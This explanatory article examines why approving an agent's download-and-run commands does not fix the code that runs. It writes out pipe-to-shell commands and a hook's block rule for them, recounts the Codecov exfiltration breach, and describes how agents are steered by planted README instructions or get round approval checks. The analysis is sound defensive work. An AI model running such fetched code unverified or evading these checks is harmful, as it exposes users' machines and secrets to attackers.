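# Approving Commands Whose Code Is Fetched at Run Time: Piped Scripts, Unpinned Packages and Mutable Tags

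## What does a person approve when a command downloads its own code?

A coding agent is a language model that a program, called the harness or sometimes the runtime, runs in a loop to work on software. The model proposes an action, such as editing a file or running a command, the harness carries it out and returns the result, and the model proposes the next action. Claude Code, made by Anthropic, and OpenAI's Codex CLI are well-known harnesses. Because a command can delete files, send data elsewhere or install software, a harness often shows the user an approval prompt before running one. The prompt displays the command and waits for a yes or no. *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026) cites a survey of 21 production agent systems, 15 of which rely on some form of approval while the agent works.

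How often the approval prompt appears depends on the harness and its settings. According to Anthropic's *Configure permissions*, the type of tool determines whether an action in Claude Code needs approval, and the permission mode the user selects determines whether a prompt appears at all. A user who answers "don't ask again" gives a standing approval, which covers later commands of the same kind.

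The approval prompt exists so that a person reading the command can catch a model that is wrong about what to run or is following instructions an attacker planted in something it read. *Approve What, Exactly?* sets two conditions for this to work: an attacker who has taken over the agent must be unable to produce the approval, and the approval must commit to exactly the action that then runs. Commands that download code can fail the second condition even when the agent is honest and the person is careful.

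### References and payloads

Suppose the prompt shows `curl -L example.com/install.sh | sh`. The first half downloads a file from a web address, and the vertical bar passes that file to `sh`, a shell, which runs its contents as commands. A person can read the whole line without seeing any of the code that the shell will run.

The web address here is a reference, a name that stands for some code. The payload is the exact bytes that run, in this case the contents of the file. Resolution turns the reference into the payload. It happens after the person has answered the prompt, and its result depends on a server the person does not control. Package names and container image labels are references too. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) describes the same situation for skills, which are bundles of instructions and scripts that users add to an agent. A reviewer sees an instruction to fetch a script,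 but the script's author can serve harmless content during the review and something else afterwards.

What a run reads can differ from what a person approved even when nothing is downloaded. In *When the Approved File Is Unchanged*, Hossen (2026) took 20 public code repositories and chose in each a file that someone might approve, such as the workflow that deploys the software. Of 5,251 commits (recorded changes to a repository), 542 altered some file that the approved run would read, and 296 of those (54.6%) left the approved file itself unchanged. Three repositories supplied 203 of the 296, so the share in any given project could be quite different. These were ordinary commits, not attacks. Hossen proposes that the approval cover every repository file the run reads, but this would not cover package registries or container images.

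### The gap between check and use

Computer security has long called this kind of problem a time-of-check to time-of-use gap, an interval between checking something and using it during which it can change. Bishop and Dilger (1996) give the standard example in *Checking for Race Conditions in File Accesses*. A Unix program running with administrator's rights has to save data for an ordinary user. It calls `access` to find out whether that user may write to a file, say `/tmp/X`, and then calls `open` to open the file for writing. Both calls take the file's name, so between them the user can delete `/tmp/X` and create a link to the system's password file under the same name. The program then writes to the password file, although it checked the old file. Several versions of `xterm`, a common terminal program, had this flaw.

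Bishop and Dilger call it a binding flaw, because the programmer wrongly assumed that a name would stay bound to one object. MITRE's *CWE-367*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, applies the idea beyond files to any resource whose state can change between check and use.

When an agent asks a person to approve a command that downloads code, the check is the person reading the text in the prompt, and the use is the later download. Bishop and Dilger say a time-of-check-to-time-of-use flaw is exploitable only if there is an interval between the check and the use, and someone untrusted can change what a name refers to during that interval. Both conditions also apply to an agent's commands.

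The time between approval and download can be a few seconds if the harness runs the command at once, or weeks under a standing approval. Anthropic states that Claude Code offers "don't ask again" only when the prompt can show everything that answer would allow. But the standing approvals that Hossen examined in Claude Code and Codex CLI match the text of a command and are not tied to the content of any file. "Everything" therefore has to mean every command the rule would allow, and it doesn't include the code those commands download later.

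As for who can change the name's meaning, Bishop and Dilger give a small piece of logic for file paths that is worth borrowing. Let w(I, o) be true if some untrusted user can change what the name o refers to during the interval I. For a file f that sits inside nested directories d₁ to dₙ, they prove:

w(I, d₁/d₂/…/dₙ/f) = w(I, d₁) ∨ w(I, d₂) ∨ … ∨ w(I, dₙ) ∨ w(I, f)

The symbol ∨ means "or", so one changeable link anywhere in the chain makes the whole name changeable. A web address also resolves through a chain (the registration of the domain, the records that point it to a server, the hosting account, the file), so it is only as stable as the least stable of these. Transitive dependencies, the packages that other packages need, add more links, each with its own publisher. On a Unix machine an administrator can inspect the permissions on every directory in a path, but a person looking at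 a prompt has no comparable way to find out who can publish to a remote name.

The agent's case differs from the Unix one in two ways, and both make it worse. The Unix program at least checked the real file, whereas a person answering a prompt usually checks only the name. The Unix attacker also has to act within a short interval, while someone who controls a download address can put the harmful version there long before the agent proposes the command. In that case, nothing changes between the approval and the download, but the person's belief about the name is out of date. That belief may rest on a script they read last year or on the project's general reputation.

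For the original flaw, MITRE suggests shortening the interval between check and use, but warns that this will not fix the problem. It also recommends locking the resource before the check, so that the resource checked is the one used. For remote code, that would mean saving a copy before the person answers the prompt, or having the approved text identify the code itself.

### Digests

A cryptographic hash function can identify the code itself. It computes a short string of fixed length, the digest, from a file of practically any length. SHA-256, the function that most tools in this field use, produces 256 bits, usually written as 64 hexadecimal characters. The same bytes always give the same digest on any machine. According to the hash standard from NIST, the US standards agency, changing a single character gives a different digest "with a very high probability".

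That qualification is there because there are only 2²⁵⁶ possible digests and many more possible files, so some different files must share a digest. The scheme is secure only if nobody can find them. NIST describes it as computationally infeasible to find a message that matches a given digest, or to find any two different messages that share one. The best general method for finding such a pair needs around 2¹²⁸ attempts, which would take a machine computing a billion billion digests per second about ten trillion years.

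Approval by digest depends on both of NIST's guarantees. The first prevents an attacker from matching the digest of a file that someone has already approved. Without the second, a script's author could prepare a harmless version and a harmful one with the same digest, submit the harmless version for approval, and swap them later.

A digest covers only the bytes that went into it. Hossen built a gate that approves a workflow file, which runs a script that reads a policy file. After the approval, Hossen edited the policy file. The workflow file's digest stayed the same, so a gate that checked only that file let the command run, and the command's output now listed administrator permissions among those it deployed. A digest over all three files did change, and the gate that checked it refused to run the command. A matching digest shows that the bytes haven't changed, but they may have been harmful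 from the start.

### Five commands compared

The table compares the script example with four other commands an agent might propose. `pip`, Python's package manager, downloads libraries from a registry and installs them. `npx` runs a JavaScript package, fetching it first if necessary. `docker run` uses a stored bundle of files, called an image, to start a container, which is a program that runs in partial isolation from the rest of the machine.

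| Command | What the approved text fixes | Who decides the rest | When |
|---|---|---|---|
| `curl -L example.com/install.sh` piped to `sh` | The address, and the fact that a shell will run whatever arrives | Whoever controls the domain, the server or the file | At each run, during the download |
| `pip install examplepkg` | The package's name | The publishers of the package and of its dependencies, with `pip` choosing among the versions they offer | During the installation |
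| `npx -y example-server` | The package's name; `-y` also answers in advance `npx`'s own question about installing it | The same kind of publishers | At any run that finds no usable copy on the machine |
| `docker run example/app:1.4` | The image's name and its tag, a label that the owner can usually move | Whoever can publish under that image name | When Docker downloads the image, by default only if the machine has no copy under that tag |
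| `docker run example/app@sha256:…` | The content of the image | Nobody, as far as the image goes; a program inside it can still download more code | Before the approval, except for anything the program fetches while it runs |

Only the last command contains a reference that always identifies the same code. The `1.4` in the fourth row looks like a fixed version, but it is a label that can be moved to different code. The pattern in the third row is common. *Scanning the Harness* (2026) found package declarations without a fixed version, typically `npx -y` followed by a bare name, in 260 of the agent setups it examined, or 9.8%. The share was 24.5% among setups that configure servers for the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting agents to outside tools. These are counts of exposed configurations, not attacks.

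### How the payload comes to change

The fetched code most often changes because its owner updates it. When a maintainer publishes a new release, such as a bug fix, every command with a floating version (a rule that admits releases not yet published) starts to fetch it. Software distribution normally works this way, and it is usually what the user wants, but it also lets a dishonest owner distribute malicious code. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* describes scripts that declare dependencies without fixing their versions. The review finds nothing because the malicious code doesn't exist until a later release. The security company SafeDep demonstrated this with `uv run`, a Python tool that resolves and installs such dependencies when the script runs, without notifying the user.

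An intruder who steals a maintainer's password or publishing token, or breaks into the server that hosts a script, can also publish different code under the existing name. Every command that relies on the name keeps working, and the owner may not find out for hours or days.

Finally, the name can pass to someone else. A domain registration lapses and a stranger buys it, or a maintainer hands a package over to a volunteer. A name can also lead to someone else's code without changing hands, if the installer looks it up in a second place. *Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised* (2026) tested an attack in which a project's setup instructions added another package index. `pip` found a package there with the same name and a higher version number and chose it, and the harness gave no warning.

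Bishop and Dilger distinguish changing an object from changing which object a name refers to, and note that either is enough to exploit the flaw when a program reads a file. The same is true of code that is about to run. The three routes also look identical in the prompt, because the approved text doesn't change. A digest in that text would expose any of them, but it would also block legitimate updates.

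### What researchers have measured

There is little direct evidence on this gap in agents. Rashidi's July 2026 survey, *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents*, sorted 39 papers into 17 categories and placed only two under time-of-check to time-of-use, *Mind the Gap* and a study of browser agents. Lilienthal and Hong (2025) describe *Mind the Gap* as the first study of time-of-check to time-of-use flaws in agents. They took 66 office-type tasks (banking, Slack, travel, workspace) from an existing benchmark and judged by hand that 56 of them left room for such a flaw, for example because the agent reads a calendar and later acts as if it had not changed. With GPT-4o, their automatic monitor caught 25% of the vulnerable sequences in the benchmark's reference solutions and 14% of those in the agent's own plans. Merging pairs of tool calls into single operations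 cut the average interval between them from 1.77 to 0.08 seconds. All their defences together lowered the share of executed runs with a flaw from 12% to 8%, a difference of about three runs on 66 tasks. They measured the intervals between one tool call and the next, so the results are weak evidence about a person who approves a download.

That count needs qualification because Rashidi assigned each paper to a single category and did not claim an exhaustive search. He also identified authorization that is "checked once and trusted forever" as a root cause in several other categories. In related work, *Temporal UI State Inconsistency in Desktop GUI Agents* (2026) measured a mean of 6.51 seconds between a desktop agent's screenshot and its next action, over only ten tasks, and *Atomicity for Agents* (2026) traces the same delay in browser agents to the time the model takes to decide. In both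 cases the agent's own information goes stale, and a faster model would shorten the delay but would not help with a standing approval given three weeks earlier.

Work on approvals themselves has increased since the survey. Hossen's October review lists at least six proposals for tying an approval more closely to what runs, including one that issues a single-use approval for the exact bytes. *Beyond Approved Actions* (2026) ties an approval to one execution and to the state of the data at that moment. If a person approves an invoice payment and the vendor is then blocked, the approval lapses. That design handles business records whose current state the system can look up. A script on a stranger's server is harder to handle because the person approving it has usually never had an earlier version to compare it with.

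## What runs when a downloaded script is piped to a shell?

The vertical bar in `curl -L example.com/install.sh | sh` runs `curl` and `sh` at the same time and connects `curl`'s output to `sh`'s input. `curl` looks up the server for example.com, requests `/install.sh` and outputs whatever comes back. The `-L` option makes it follow redirects, so the file may come from a different address than the one in the prompt. Because the command gives `sh` no file to read, `sh` takes its commands from standard input, according to the *sh(1p)* page of the POSIX Programmer's Manual. Here, standard input is `curl`'s output.

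The shell runs each command as soon as it has read it, so the first lines of a script can be changing the machine while the server is still sending the last ones. Neither program saves a copy. Monperrus (2026), in *Practical Agentic Software Supply Chain Security*, points out that nobody can therefore inspect the script or compute its digest before it runs. Nobody can examine it afterwards either.

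If the connection breaks halfway, the machine is left with a partial installation. The shell will also try to run the last line it received, even if that line is incomplete (nybble41, 2022, in *The malicious "rustdecimal" crate*, a comment thread on the Linux news site LWN). If the script contains `rm -rf /opt/example/cache`, which deletes one folder, and the stream stops after `/opt`, the shell deletes everything under `/opt`. The shell's `pipefail` option makes a pipeline report failure when any part of it fails, but it doesn't prevent this because the report comes after the commands have run.

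Careful publishers guard against partial downloads by putting the whole script inside a function and calling the function on the last line. If the download stops partway through the function, the shell has nothing complete to run. Docker's install script does this, and a comment in it describes the function as "some protection against only getting half the file".

Piping also interferes with an installer's prompts, because standard input is carrying the script instead of the user's answers. The script for rustup, which installs the Rust programming language, avoids this by connecting its installer directly to the user's terminal. If it finds no terminal, it stops and suggests adding `-y`, which turns off the installer's own confirmation prompt. A coding agent often runs commands without a terminal and is likely to follow that suggestion, leaving the harness's approval prompt as the only one.

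### What HTTPS protects

When the address begins with `https://`, `curl` checks that the server holds a valid certificate for the domain, and encryption stops anyone along the route from reading or altering the file. The address in the example above lacks this prefix, so `curl` makes its first request over plain HTTP, which gives neither protection.

HTTPS secures the connection but doesn't control what the server sends. In the short note *Making curl|bash suck a tiny bit less*, jdarcy (2016) points out that HTTPS protects against interception but not against an attack on the server the script comes from. The certificate stays valid whether an intruder or the owner replaces the file. A server can also send different content to different visitors.

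Many install commands fetch a script from a GitHub address that contains a branch name, often `main`, the usual name of a repository's principal branch. Such an address leads to the newest version of the file on that branch, which can change with any commit. GitHub's *Getting permanent links to files* recommends replacing the branch name with a commit ID, a long identifier for one recorded state of the repository, so that the file at that address will not change. This is an easy improvement, and the user can see it in the approval prompt. But `curl` doesn't check the file against the ID, so the user still relies on GitHub to send the right file.

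### Reading the script first

A careful person might read the script in a browser, find nothing wrong and then approve the piped command. The command downloads the script again before the shell runs it. The second copy is usually identical to the first, but it differs if the maintainer published a change in the meantime or the server sends something else the second time. An agent that fetches a script, reads it and then proposes the piped command has the same problem. In March, Lavi (2026) reported for the security firm Arnica that a coding agent could run a different script from the one it had inspected (*Bypassing Cursor Agents Guardrails through a Script Inspection Design Flaw*). The agent's vendor ruled the report out of scope.

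The inspection is arguably worse than no inspection here, because it gives the person a reason to approve that doesn't apply to the code that runs.

### The case for piping

Many respectable projects tell users to pipe a script to a shell, and some have defended the practice. The best-known defence is *Is curl|bash insecure?* (Varda, 2015), written for Sandstorm, a security product that people installed this way. Varda mainly argues that anything a user installs could do as much damage as a piped script. Traditional Unix software runs with all the permissions of the user who starts it, and most package managers run scripts from the package as the administrator during installation. He says a piped script looks alarming because it makes this obvious.

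Varda takes a second objection more seriously, that a third party might replace the download. He replies that relying on HTTPS was normal practice for Firefox, Chrome and Rust installers and for downloads of whole Linux systems, and that npm, the JavaScript package manager, had no other integrity protection at the time. He still agrees that a second safeguard is worth having, and Sandstorm began to offer installation with a signature check on the day the essay appeared. He notes that a signature adds protection only if the user gets the signing key from somewhere other than the developer's server.

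Tournoij, a programmer who later made a similar argument, compares piping with the usual alternative, copying a project's source code and building it. He notes that almost nobody reads the build files, which can run to tens of thousands of generated lines, and that nobody considers this malpractice. He thinks it hardly matters if a server sends `curl` a different script from the one a browser gets, because the user already trusts the vendor and is about to run its software anyway. He concedes that package managers are more secure because of checksums, signing and auditing, and advises using a package where one exists.

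Piping a script to a shell seems to add little risk over running any other installer from the same site if the user knows the publisher, takes the address from its documentation and runs the command once. Even *Unverified Script Execution*, which documents a rule in poutine, a scanner for automated build pipelines, says that piping is generally safe when the source is trusted.

When a coding agent asks for approval, the user may not have chosen the publisher. The model proposes the address, which it may have found in a file that an attacker wrote. Monperrus gives the example of a package whose README recommends an extra command "for best performance", which an agent may run while setting up the project. Tournoij assumes that the user already trusts the vendor, but at the prompt the user still has to decide whether to trust it. Someone who reads the script to make that decision can't rely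 on the argument that a trusted server would have no need to send a different one.

Varda's comparison is also weaker support for approving piped scripts than it seems. If a piped script is no worse than a package installation, then the approval prompt for the installation deserves the same doubt, because neither prompt ties the approval to specific code.

### The Codecov uploader

The Codecov breach of 2021 is a good test of the argument from trust because the publisher was honest and the connection was secure. Codecov measures how much of a program's code its tests run. Customers uploaded their results with a script called the Bash Uploader, which their continuous integration systems (servers that build and test software automatically) repeatedly downloaded and ran.

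According to Codecov's *Post-Mortem / Root Cause Analysis (April 2021)*, an attacker found a storage key in one of the company's public Docker images and used it to alter the script that customers downloaded from cloud storage. The change was a single line that sent the environment variables of any machine that ran the script, along with the address of the customer's repository, to a server outside the company. Build systems commonly keep passwords and access tokens in these variables.

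The alterations began on 31 January 2021 and ended on 1 April. Codecov's *Bash Uploader Security Update* (2021) reports 108 separate windows in which the script was altered. Codecov doesn't explain why the line came and went, but a customer who read the script before running it could have seen a clean copy in February and run an altered one later.

A customer discovered the breach by comparing checksums, which are digests that a publisher posts so that users can check their copies against them. Codecov kept the checksums for its script on GitHub. On the morning of 1 April, the customer found that the SHA-256 digest of its downloaded script did not match the one on GitHub and reported this to Codecov. The company removed the line that day and told affected customers on 15 April. CISA's *Codecov Releases Security Update* (2021), an alert from the US cybersecurity agency, repeats these dates.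 According to Codecov, customers who had compared checksums before each run may not have been affected.

Few users seem to have validated Codecov's script before running it. Codecov admitted it had never properly documented the check. After the disclosure, Stinner (2021), in *Code coverage on the CI*, noted that the Python project's own test systems were downloading and running the script without validating it. Some victims had never typed the download command themselves, because Codecov's add-ons for GitHub, CircleCI and Bitrise used the same script.

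Varda could fairly reply that a compiled installer in the same storage would have been just as easy to alter. The customers who were safe had compared the file with a record that the attacker couldn't change, a check that works with any file format. Codecov was more critical of piped installation, calling it "incredibly convenient" but full of security problems, and replaced the script with a signed program.

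### Downloading once

The remedy for the second download is to make only one. The following commands save the script, compute its digest, display it and run the saved copy:

```
curl -fsSL https://example.com/install.sh -o install.sh
sha256sum install.sh
cat install.sh
echo "DIGEST  install.sh" | sha256sum -c - && sh install.sh
```

In the first line, `-o` names the file to write and `-f` makes `curl` fail if the server returns an error page. A broken connection now produces an error message instead of a partial installation, since nothing has run yet. The second line prints the 64-character digest that replaces `DIGEST` in the last line. There, `sha256sum -c` recomputes the digest and compares the two, and `&&` runs the script only if they match.

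A harness could run the first three lines without much risk and ask the person to approve the fourth, showing the script beside it. The approved text would contain the digest, so it would identify the file's bytes as well as its name. Even a standing approval of that line would cover only that one script. In its installation guide, Docker recommends a shorter version without the digest: save the script, read it, and run the saved file.

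Few people will read several hundred lines of shell script at a prompt, and hardly anyone can judge a digest by looking at it. A colleague, a scanner or another model can review the script instead, and the machine can then use the digest to check that the file about to run is the one they reviewed. A saved copy also helps after a compromise. Codecov told customers who had kept a local copy of its uploader to search it for the malicious line, but customers who had only piped the script had no copy to search.

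The last line still has a small time-of-check to time-of-use gap. Another program on the machine could overwrite `install.sh` after the comparison but before `sh` opens it, much like the old Unix flaw with `/tmp/X`. The harness can close the gap by storing the file where neither the agent nor any other program can write to it.

### Whose digest?

Downloading a script once and recording its digest can also pin a malicious version. This would have happened to a Codecov customer who first downloaded the uploader during one of the 108 windows when it was compromised.

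A publisher's checksum can reveal an altered script, but Monperrus notes that publishers rarely provide checksums and that they are worthless if the attacker also controls the place they come from. If `install.sh` and `install.sh.sha256` are on the same server, whoever replaces one can replace the other. Codecov's checksums revealed the alteration because the stolen key gave access to the cloud storage but not to GitHub, where the checksums were.

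*Validating the Bash Script on CI* (Hu, 2021), published for Codecov's customers a month later, describes a procedure that relies on the same separation. The customer's system saves the script to a file, reads the version number from it, fetches the checksums for that version from GitHub, checks the file against them and then runs it. Unlike a recorded digest, this keeps working when Codecov updates the script, which Hu says happened constantly. It accepts any script that matches checksums Codecov has published on GitHub, including an old release with a known flaw, because the version number comes from the downloaded file itself. Sandstorm handled that problem separately, with an installer that refused releases more than a month old.

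The publisher's checksum is useful when a person first decides whether to approve the command, and the recorded digest is useful each time the command runs after that.

### Scripts that download more

Many install scripts are short programs that fetch a longer one. The rustup script detects the machine's processor and operating system, downloads the matching `rustup-init` program, marks it as executable and runs it. The script requires HTTPS where the download tool supports it, but does not check the program against a digest. Unless the user sets a version, the download URL has no version number, so two runs of a script with the same digest can install different programs.

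On Ubuntu and Debian, Docker's script goes further, adding Docker's package repository to the system and installing seven packages, in their latest stable versions by default, plus their dependencies. The package manager checks the packages against a signing key, but the script downloads that key from the same server as the packages, which is the arrangement Varda warned against. An attacker who controlled the server during installation could supply both the key and the packages.

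Docker also offers a `--dry-run` option, which prints the script's steps without running them. This helps someone who trusts the script and wants to know what it will do to the machine. But the option is part of the script, so an altered script could ignore it, and Docker's example uses the option with administrator rights.

To cover what rustup installs, a person would also have to approve the digest of `rustup-init`. It is simpler to skip the script, download `rustup-init` directly and apply the four commands to that file. However, a compiled program is much harder to read than a script, and `rustup-init` itself downloads the Rust tools. Cutting off the network during the run would at least turn an unapproved download into an error.

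### A rule that blocks the pipe

Some developers have tried to stop agents from piping downloads to a shell. In June 2026, Monperrus, of the KTH Royal Institute of Technology, published a rule that does this for Claude Code. It uses a hook, a small program that users can install to run before each of Claude Code's actions and block it if necessary. The hook passes every shell command to Semgrep, a tool that parses code into its grammatical structure, and blocks the command if `curl` or `wget` (another download program) is piped to any of ten listed shells. Monperrus argues that a plain text search would be less reliable because the same command can be written with different options, quoting and line breaks. When a command is blocked, the agent receives a message with instructions to download the script, inspect it and then execute it.

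He tested the hook on seven commands:

| Download command | Where the script goes | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `curl -fsSL` with a GitHub address | `bash` | blocked |
| `wget -qO-` | `bash` | blocked |
| `curl` | `sh` | blocked |
| `curl` | `zsh` | blocked |
| `wget` with `-O -` | `bash` | blocked |
| `curl` with `-o /tmp/install.sh` | a file | allowed |
| `echo hello` | nowhere, as it downloads nothing | allowed |

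The results show that the rule recognises the plain form of the pattern. Neither allowed command contains a pipe, so the test doesn't show whether the rule allows harmless pipes, such as one that sends a download to a data formatter. The test also omits the form that Codecov's customers had in their build files, `bash <(curl …)`, which passes the download to the shell as if it were a file. The rule's pattern doesn't appear to cover this form because it isn't a pipeline.

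Monperrus acknowledges a larger limit. The hook allows an agent to download the script with one command and run it with the next. He considers this a modest gain, because it leaves a file that a person or the agent can read, but not a guarantee of security.

It may even leave the person at the prompt worse off. The second command, `bash /tmp/install.sh`, no longer shows where the code came from, and the file can change before the command runs. If the agent joins the two commands on one line, nobody has a chance to read the file before it runs. The rule removes the second download only if the agent runs the same file it read, and the hook doesn't check this.

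The poutine rule mentioned earlier comes closer to what an approval needs. It reports any script or program that a build pipeline downloads and then executes without verifying its integrity, whether or not the download is piped to an interpreter, and whether that interpreter is a shell, Python or PHP. But poutine examines a build definition that already contains every command. A hook in a coding agent receives one command at a time, so to apply the same test it would have to keep a record of the files that earlier commands downloaded.

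## How does a package install choose its code, and what does a lockfile fix?

Tournoij's advice to use a package where one exists has some merit. A package manager saves the whole archive before unpacking it, so a broken connection can't leave the machine running half a script, and it can check the archive against a digest. But the name in `npm install examplelib` is still a reference, and to resolve it the package manager must choose a version, a step that a script address doesn't need.

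A package install chooses its code from a registry, a central server to which publishers upload their releases. The npm registry for JavaScript held more than 3 million packages and 25 million releases in September 2024, according to *Pinning Is Futile* (He, Vasilescu and Kästner, 2025). A publisher there can't use the same version number twice, so version 1.2.3 of a package keeps its content for as long as it exists. However, the approved command often doesn't determine which version will be installed. If the command gives no version, npm normally installs the release labelled `latest`, and the publisher's label usually moves to each new release. According to npm's documentation, npm installs a different release if the latest one doesn't support the installed version of Node.js, the program that runs JavaScript outside a browser. The same approved command can therefore install different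 code on two machines at the same moment.

### Version ranges

A project normally lists the packages it uses in a file, such as npm's `package.json`, with a version rule for each. The rules rely on a convention called semantic versioning. In version 1.2.3, the 1 is the major number, the 2 is the minor number and the 3 is the patch number. A publisher is supposed to raise the major number for changes that break existing programs, the minor number for new features and the patch number for bug fixes.

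| Rule in `package.json` | Versions it admits |
|---|---|
| `1.2.0` | 1.2.0 only |
| `~1.2.0` | From 1.2.0 up to, but not including, 1.3.0 |
| `^1.2.0` | From 1.2.0 up to, but not including, 2.0.0 |
| `>=1.2.0` | 1.2.0 and every later version, including new major versions |

Every row except the top one is a floating version. The caret is npm's default. Even when someone approves `npm install examplelib@1.2.3`, npm installs that version but, unless the command includes `--save-exact`, writes `^1.2.3` into `package.json`. That range also allows later versions, which the approval didn't cover.

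The notation also differs between tools. Cargo, Rust's package manager, treats a plain `1.2.0` in its configuration file as `^1.2.0` and requires an equals sign for an exact version. In pip, an exact version is written `==1.2.0`. A person reading a project's requirements at an approval prompt needs to know which tool will interpret them.

Semantic versioning is only a promise by the publisher. Nothing in the registry prevents someone from putting a breaking change, or malicious code, into a release numbered as a bug fix.

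### How a resolver picks versions

Most of the code in an installation comes from packages that nobody named in the command. He et al. note that an npm project commonly has orders of magnitude more transitive dependencies than direct ones. The package manager's resolver selects the versions. It reads the project's version rules, looks up the available versions in the registry and picks one that fits each rule, usually the newest. It then reads the rules in the packages it picked and repeats the process until no dependencies are left to resolve.

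Two packages may need different versions of a third package, and npm can install both versions. In an example from its documentation, package A needs B and C, B needs version 1 of D, and C needs version 2 of D. npm puts D 1 in the main folder, where B finds it, and D 2 in a private folder inside C. npm tries to avoid such duplicates, but finding the arrangement with the fewest is an NP-complete problem, which means no known method is fast in every case, so it uses rules of thumb. According to the documentation, requesting the same packages in a different order can produce a different result.

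Python normally allows only one version of a package in an environment, so pip has to find a set of versions that meets every requirement. If its choice leads to a conflict, it goes back and tries an older version. To learn a version's dependencies, pip may have to download it and, if the publisher offers only source code, run part of that code. A release that pip eventually rejects can therefore still run code on the machine.

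### One install by the clock

Suppose a project's `package.json` contains the line `"examplelib": "^1.2.0"` and the project has no lockfile. A coding agent proposes `npm install`, which installs the dependencies listed in `package.json`.

| Time | Event | Newest version the rule admits |
|---|---|---|
| 10:00 | The harness shows the prompt | 1.2.3 |
| 10:02 | The developer looks up `examplelib`, sees that 1.2.3 is a month old, and approves | 1.2.3 |
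| 10:03 | The harness waits for a test run to finish | 1.2.3 |
| 10:05 | The publisher releases 1.3.0 | 1.3.0 |
| 10:09 | The command runs and installs 1.3.0 | 1.3.0 |

The developer checked the version that the command would have installed at 10:02. npm followed its rules, and the approved text had not changed. If the publisher had released 2.0.0 instead, the command would still have installed 1.2.3. With `~1.2.0`, npm would have ignored 1.3.0 but accepted 1.2.4.

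An exact version closes this gap for `examplelib` but not for its dependencies. An older page of npm's documentation explains that if A requires an exact version of B, and B accepts a range of versions of C, the author of A can't refuse a new release of C when B hasn't changed. In the example, a new release of such a dependency at 10:05 would also have reached the machine at 10:09.

npm has an option, `--before`, that makes the resolver ignore every release published after a given date. A harness could add the time of the approval to the command, and the 10:05 release would then no longer count, either for `examplelib` or for its dependencies. This is a cheap improvement, although it identifies the code only indirectly. It relies on the registry's record of when each release appeared, and a publisher who withdraws a version can still change the result.

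### Install scripts

A package can include install scripts, named `preinstall`, `install` and `postinstall`, which npm runs during installation with the permissions of the user who started it. They typically compile a component for the machine or download a prebuilt one. A developer who installs a library and then reads its code before using it has already run these scripts. GitHub, which owns npm, says attackers use install scripts to steal credentials immediately instead of waiting for someone to run the package.

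npm used to run these scripts for every dependency without asking. That changed with version 12, which came out in July 2026, according to GitHub's *npm install-time security and GAT bypass2fa deprecation* (2026). The details are in GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026). Unless the project explicitly allows them, npm no longer runs:

- `preinstall`, `install` and `postinstall` scripts from dependencies;
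- the compilation that npm starts by itself for a package with a `binding.gyp` file, even if the package declares no script;
- `prepare` scripts from dependencies that come from a Git repository, a local file or a link.

Version 12 also refuses by default to fetch dependencies from Git repositories or from web addresses outside the registry. GitHub explains that a Git dependency could include a configuration file that replaced the Git program npm used, letting an attacker run code even when the user had turned scripts off.

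A developer allows a script with `npm approve-scripts`, which adds the package to a list in `package.json`. The approval carries over to later installs, but by default npm records the package with its version, such as `canvas@1.2.3`, so a later release needs a new approval. The command can also approve every waiting script at once (`--all`) or any future version of a package (`--no-allow-scripts-pin`). When a skipped script leaves a package broken, an agent may well propose one of these broader forms to get the build running, and the person approving its commands should check for them.

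The new default doesn't stop all fetched code from running. Because it applies only to dependencies, it doesn't cover scripts in the project's own `package.json`, which matters when an agent has just copied a stranger's project. Older versions of npm still run every install script. A package that can't run code during installation can still run it when a program imports it. This may happen only seconds later, because coding agents often run a project's tests right after an install. With `npx` there is hardly any delay, because the command's purpose is to run the package.

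In *For sixteen years, npm install executed arbitrary code shipped by any*, a personal blog post, Robert writes that Go has never run dependency code at install time and that pnpm and Bun, two alternative JavaScript package managers, have blocked it since January 2025. He considers the risk on PyPI, Python's registry, mostly neutralised by wheels, which are packages that the publisher has already built and pip only has to unpack. But if no suitable wheel exists, pip builds the package from source, which runs the package's build code. The option `--only-binary :all:` makes pip refuse packages without a suitable wheel.

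### What a lockfile records

A lockfile stores the resolver's answers, so that the next installation doesn't have to ask the questions again. The package manager writes it automatically, and developers usually keep it in the project's repository. Gamage, Tiwari and colleagues (2025), in *The Design Space of Lockfiles Across Package Managers*, reproduce part of the npm lockfile of Modelina, an open-source tool that generates data models. The entry for one package, `@apidevtools/json-schema-ref-parser`, has these fields:

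| Field | Value |
|---|---|
| `version` | 11.1.1 |
| `resolved` | The address of the package's archive on `registry.npmjs.org` |
| `integrity` | `sha512-WZyqzPLrWctQB8qB8uGivvzWg…` (cut short here) |
| `dependencies` | `@jsdevtools/ono`, with the rule `^7.1.3` |

Modelina's `package.json` asks for `^11.1.0`, and the lockfile records that the resolver chose 11.1.1. The `integrity` value is the SHA-512 digest of the package's archive. The full value has 88 characters because npm uses a more compact notation than the hexadecimal one described earlier. If a downloaded archive has a different digest, npm stops with an error. The last row contains a range because npm copied the package's own requirements. A separate entry records the version of `@jsdevtools/ono` that the resolver chose.

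The digest also makes the `resolved` address less important. npm's *package-lock.json* explains that npm treats `registry.npmjs.org` in this field as a placeholder for whichever registry the user has configured. A company can therefore use its own copy of the registry with the same lockfile, and the archives must still match their digests. Some entries may have SHA-1 digests, which give weaker protection because researchers have found different files with the same SHA-1 digest. An entry also has a `hasInstallScript` flag if its package has an install script, so a harness could list all such packages before downloading any of them.

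Because the lockfile contains a digest of each archive, a single digest of the lockfile covers them all. Changing any package means changing its entry, which changes the lockfile's digest. If the repository files covered by an approval under Hossen's proposal include a lockfile, and the command obeys it, the approval also fixes the content of hundreds of archives in a package registry. The approval should also cover `.npmrc`, npm's configuration file, because its settings can turn install scripts and Git dependencies back on.

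Six of the seven package managers that Gamage and colleagues studied record digests in their lockfiles. The exception is Gradle, a Java tool, whose lockfile contains only names and versions.

### Commands that obey the lockfile and commands that don't

Having a lockfile in the project doesn't mean the approved command will follow it.

| Command | What it does with a lockfile | Can a release published after the approval change what it installs? |
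|---|---|---|
| `npm ci` | Installs what the lockfile lists and stops if the lockfile is missing or conflicts with `package.json` | No |
| `npm install` | Follows the lockfile where it fits `package.json`, and otherwise resolves again and rewrites it | Yes, where the two conflict or there is no lockfile |
| `npm install examplelib` | Resolves the name and updates the lockfile | Yes |
| `npx examplelib` | Uses the project's own copy if there is one | Yes, if it has to download the package |
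| `npm install -g examplelib` | Uses none, because it installs outside any project | Yes |
| `pip install examplelib` | Uses none | Yes |
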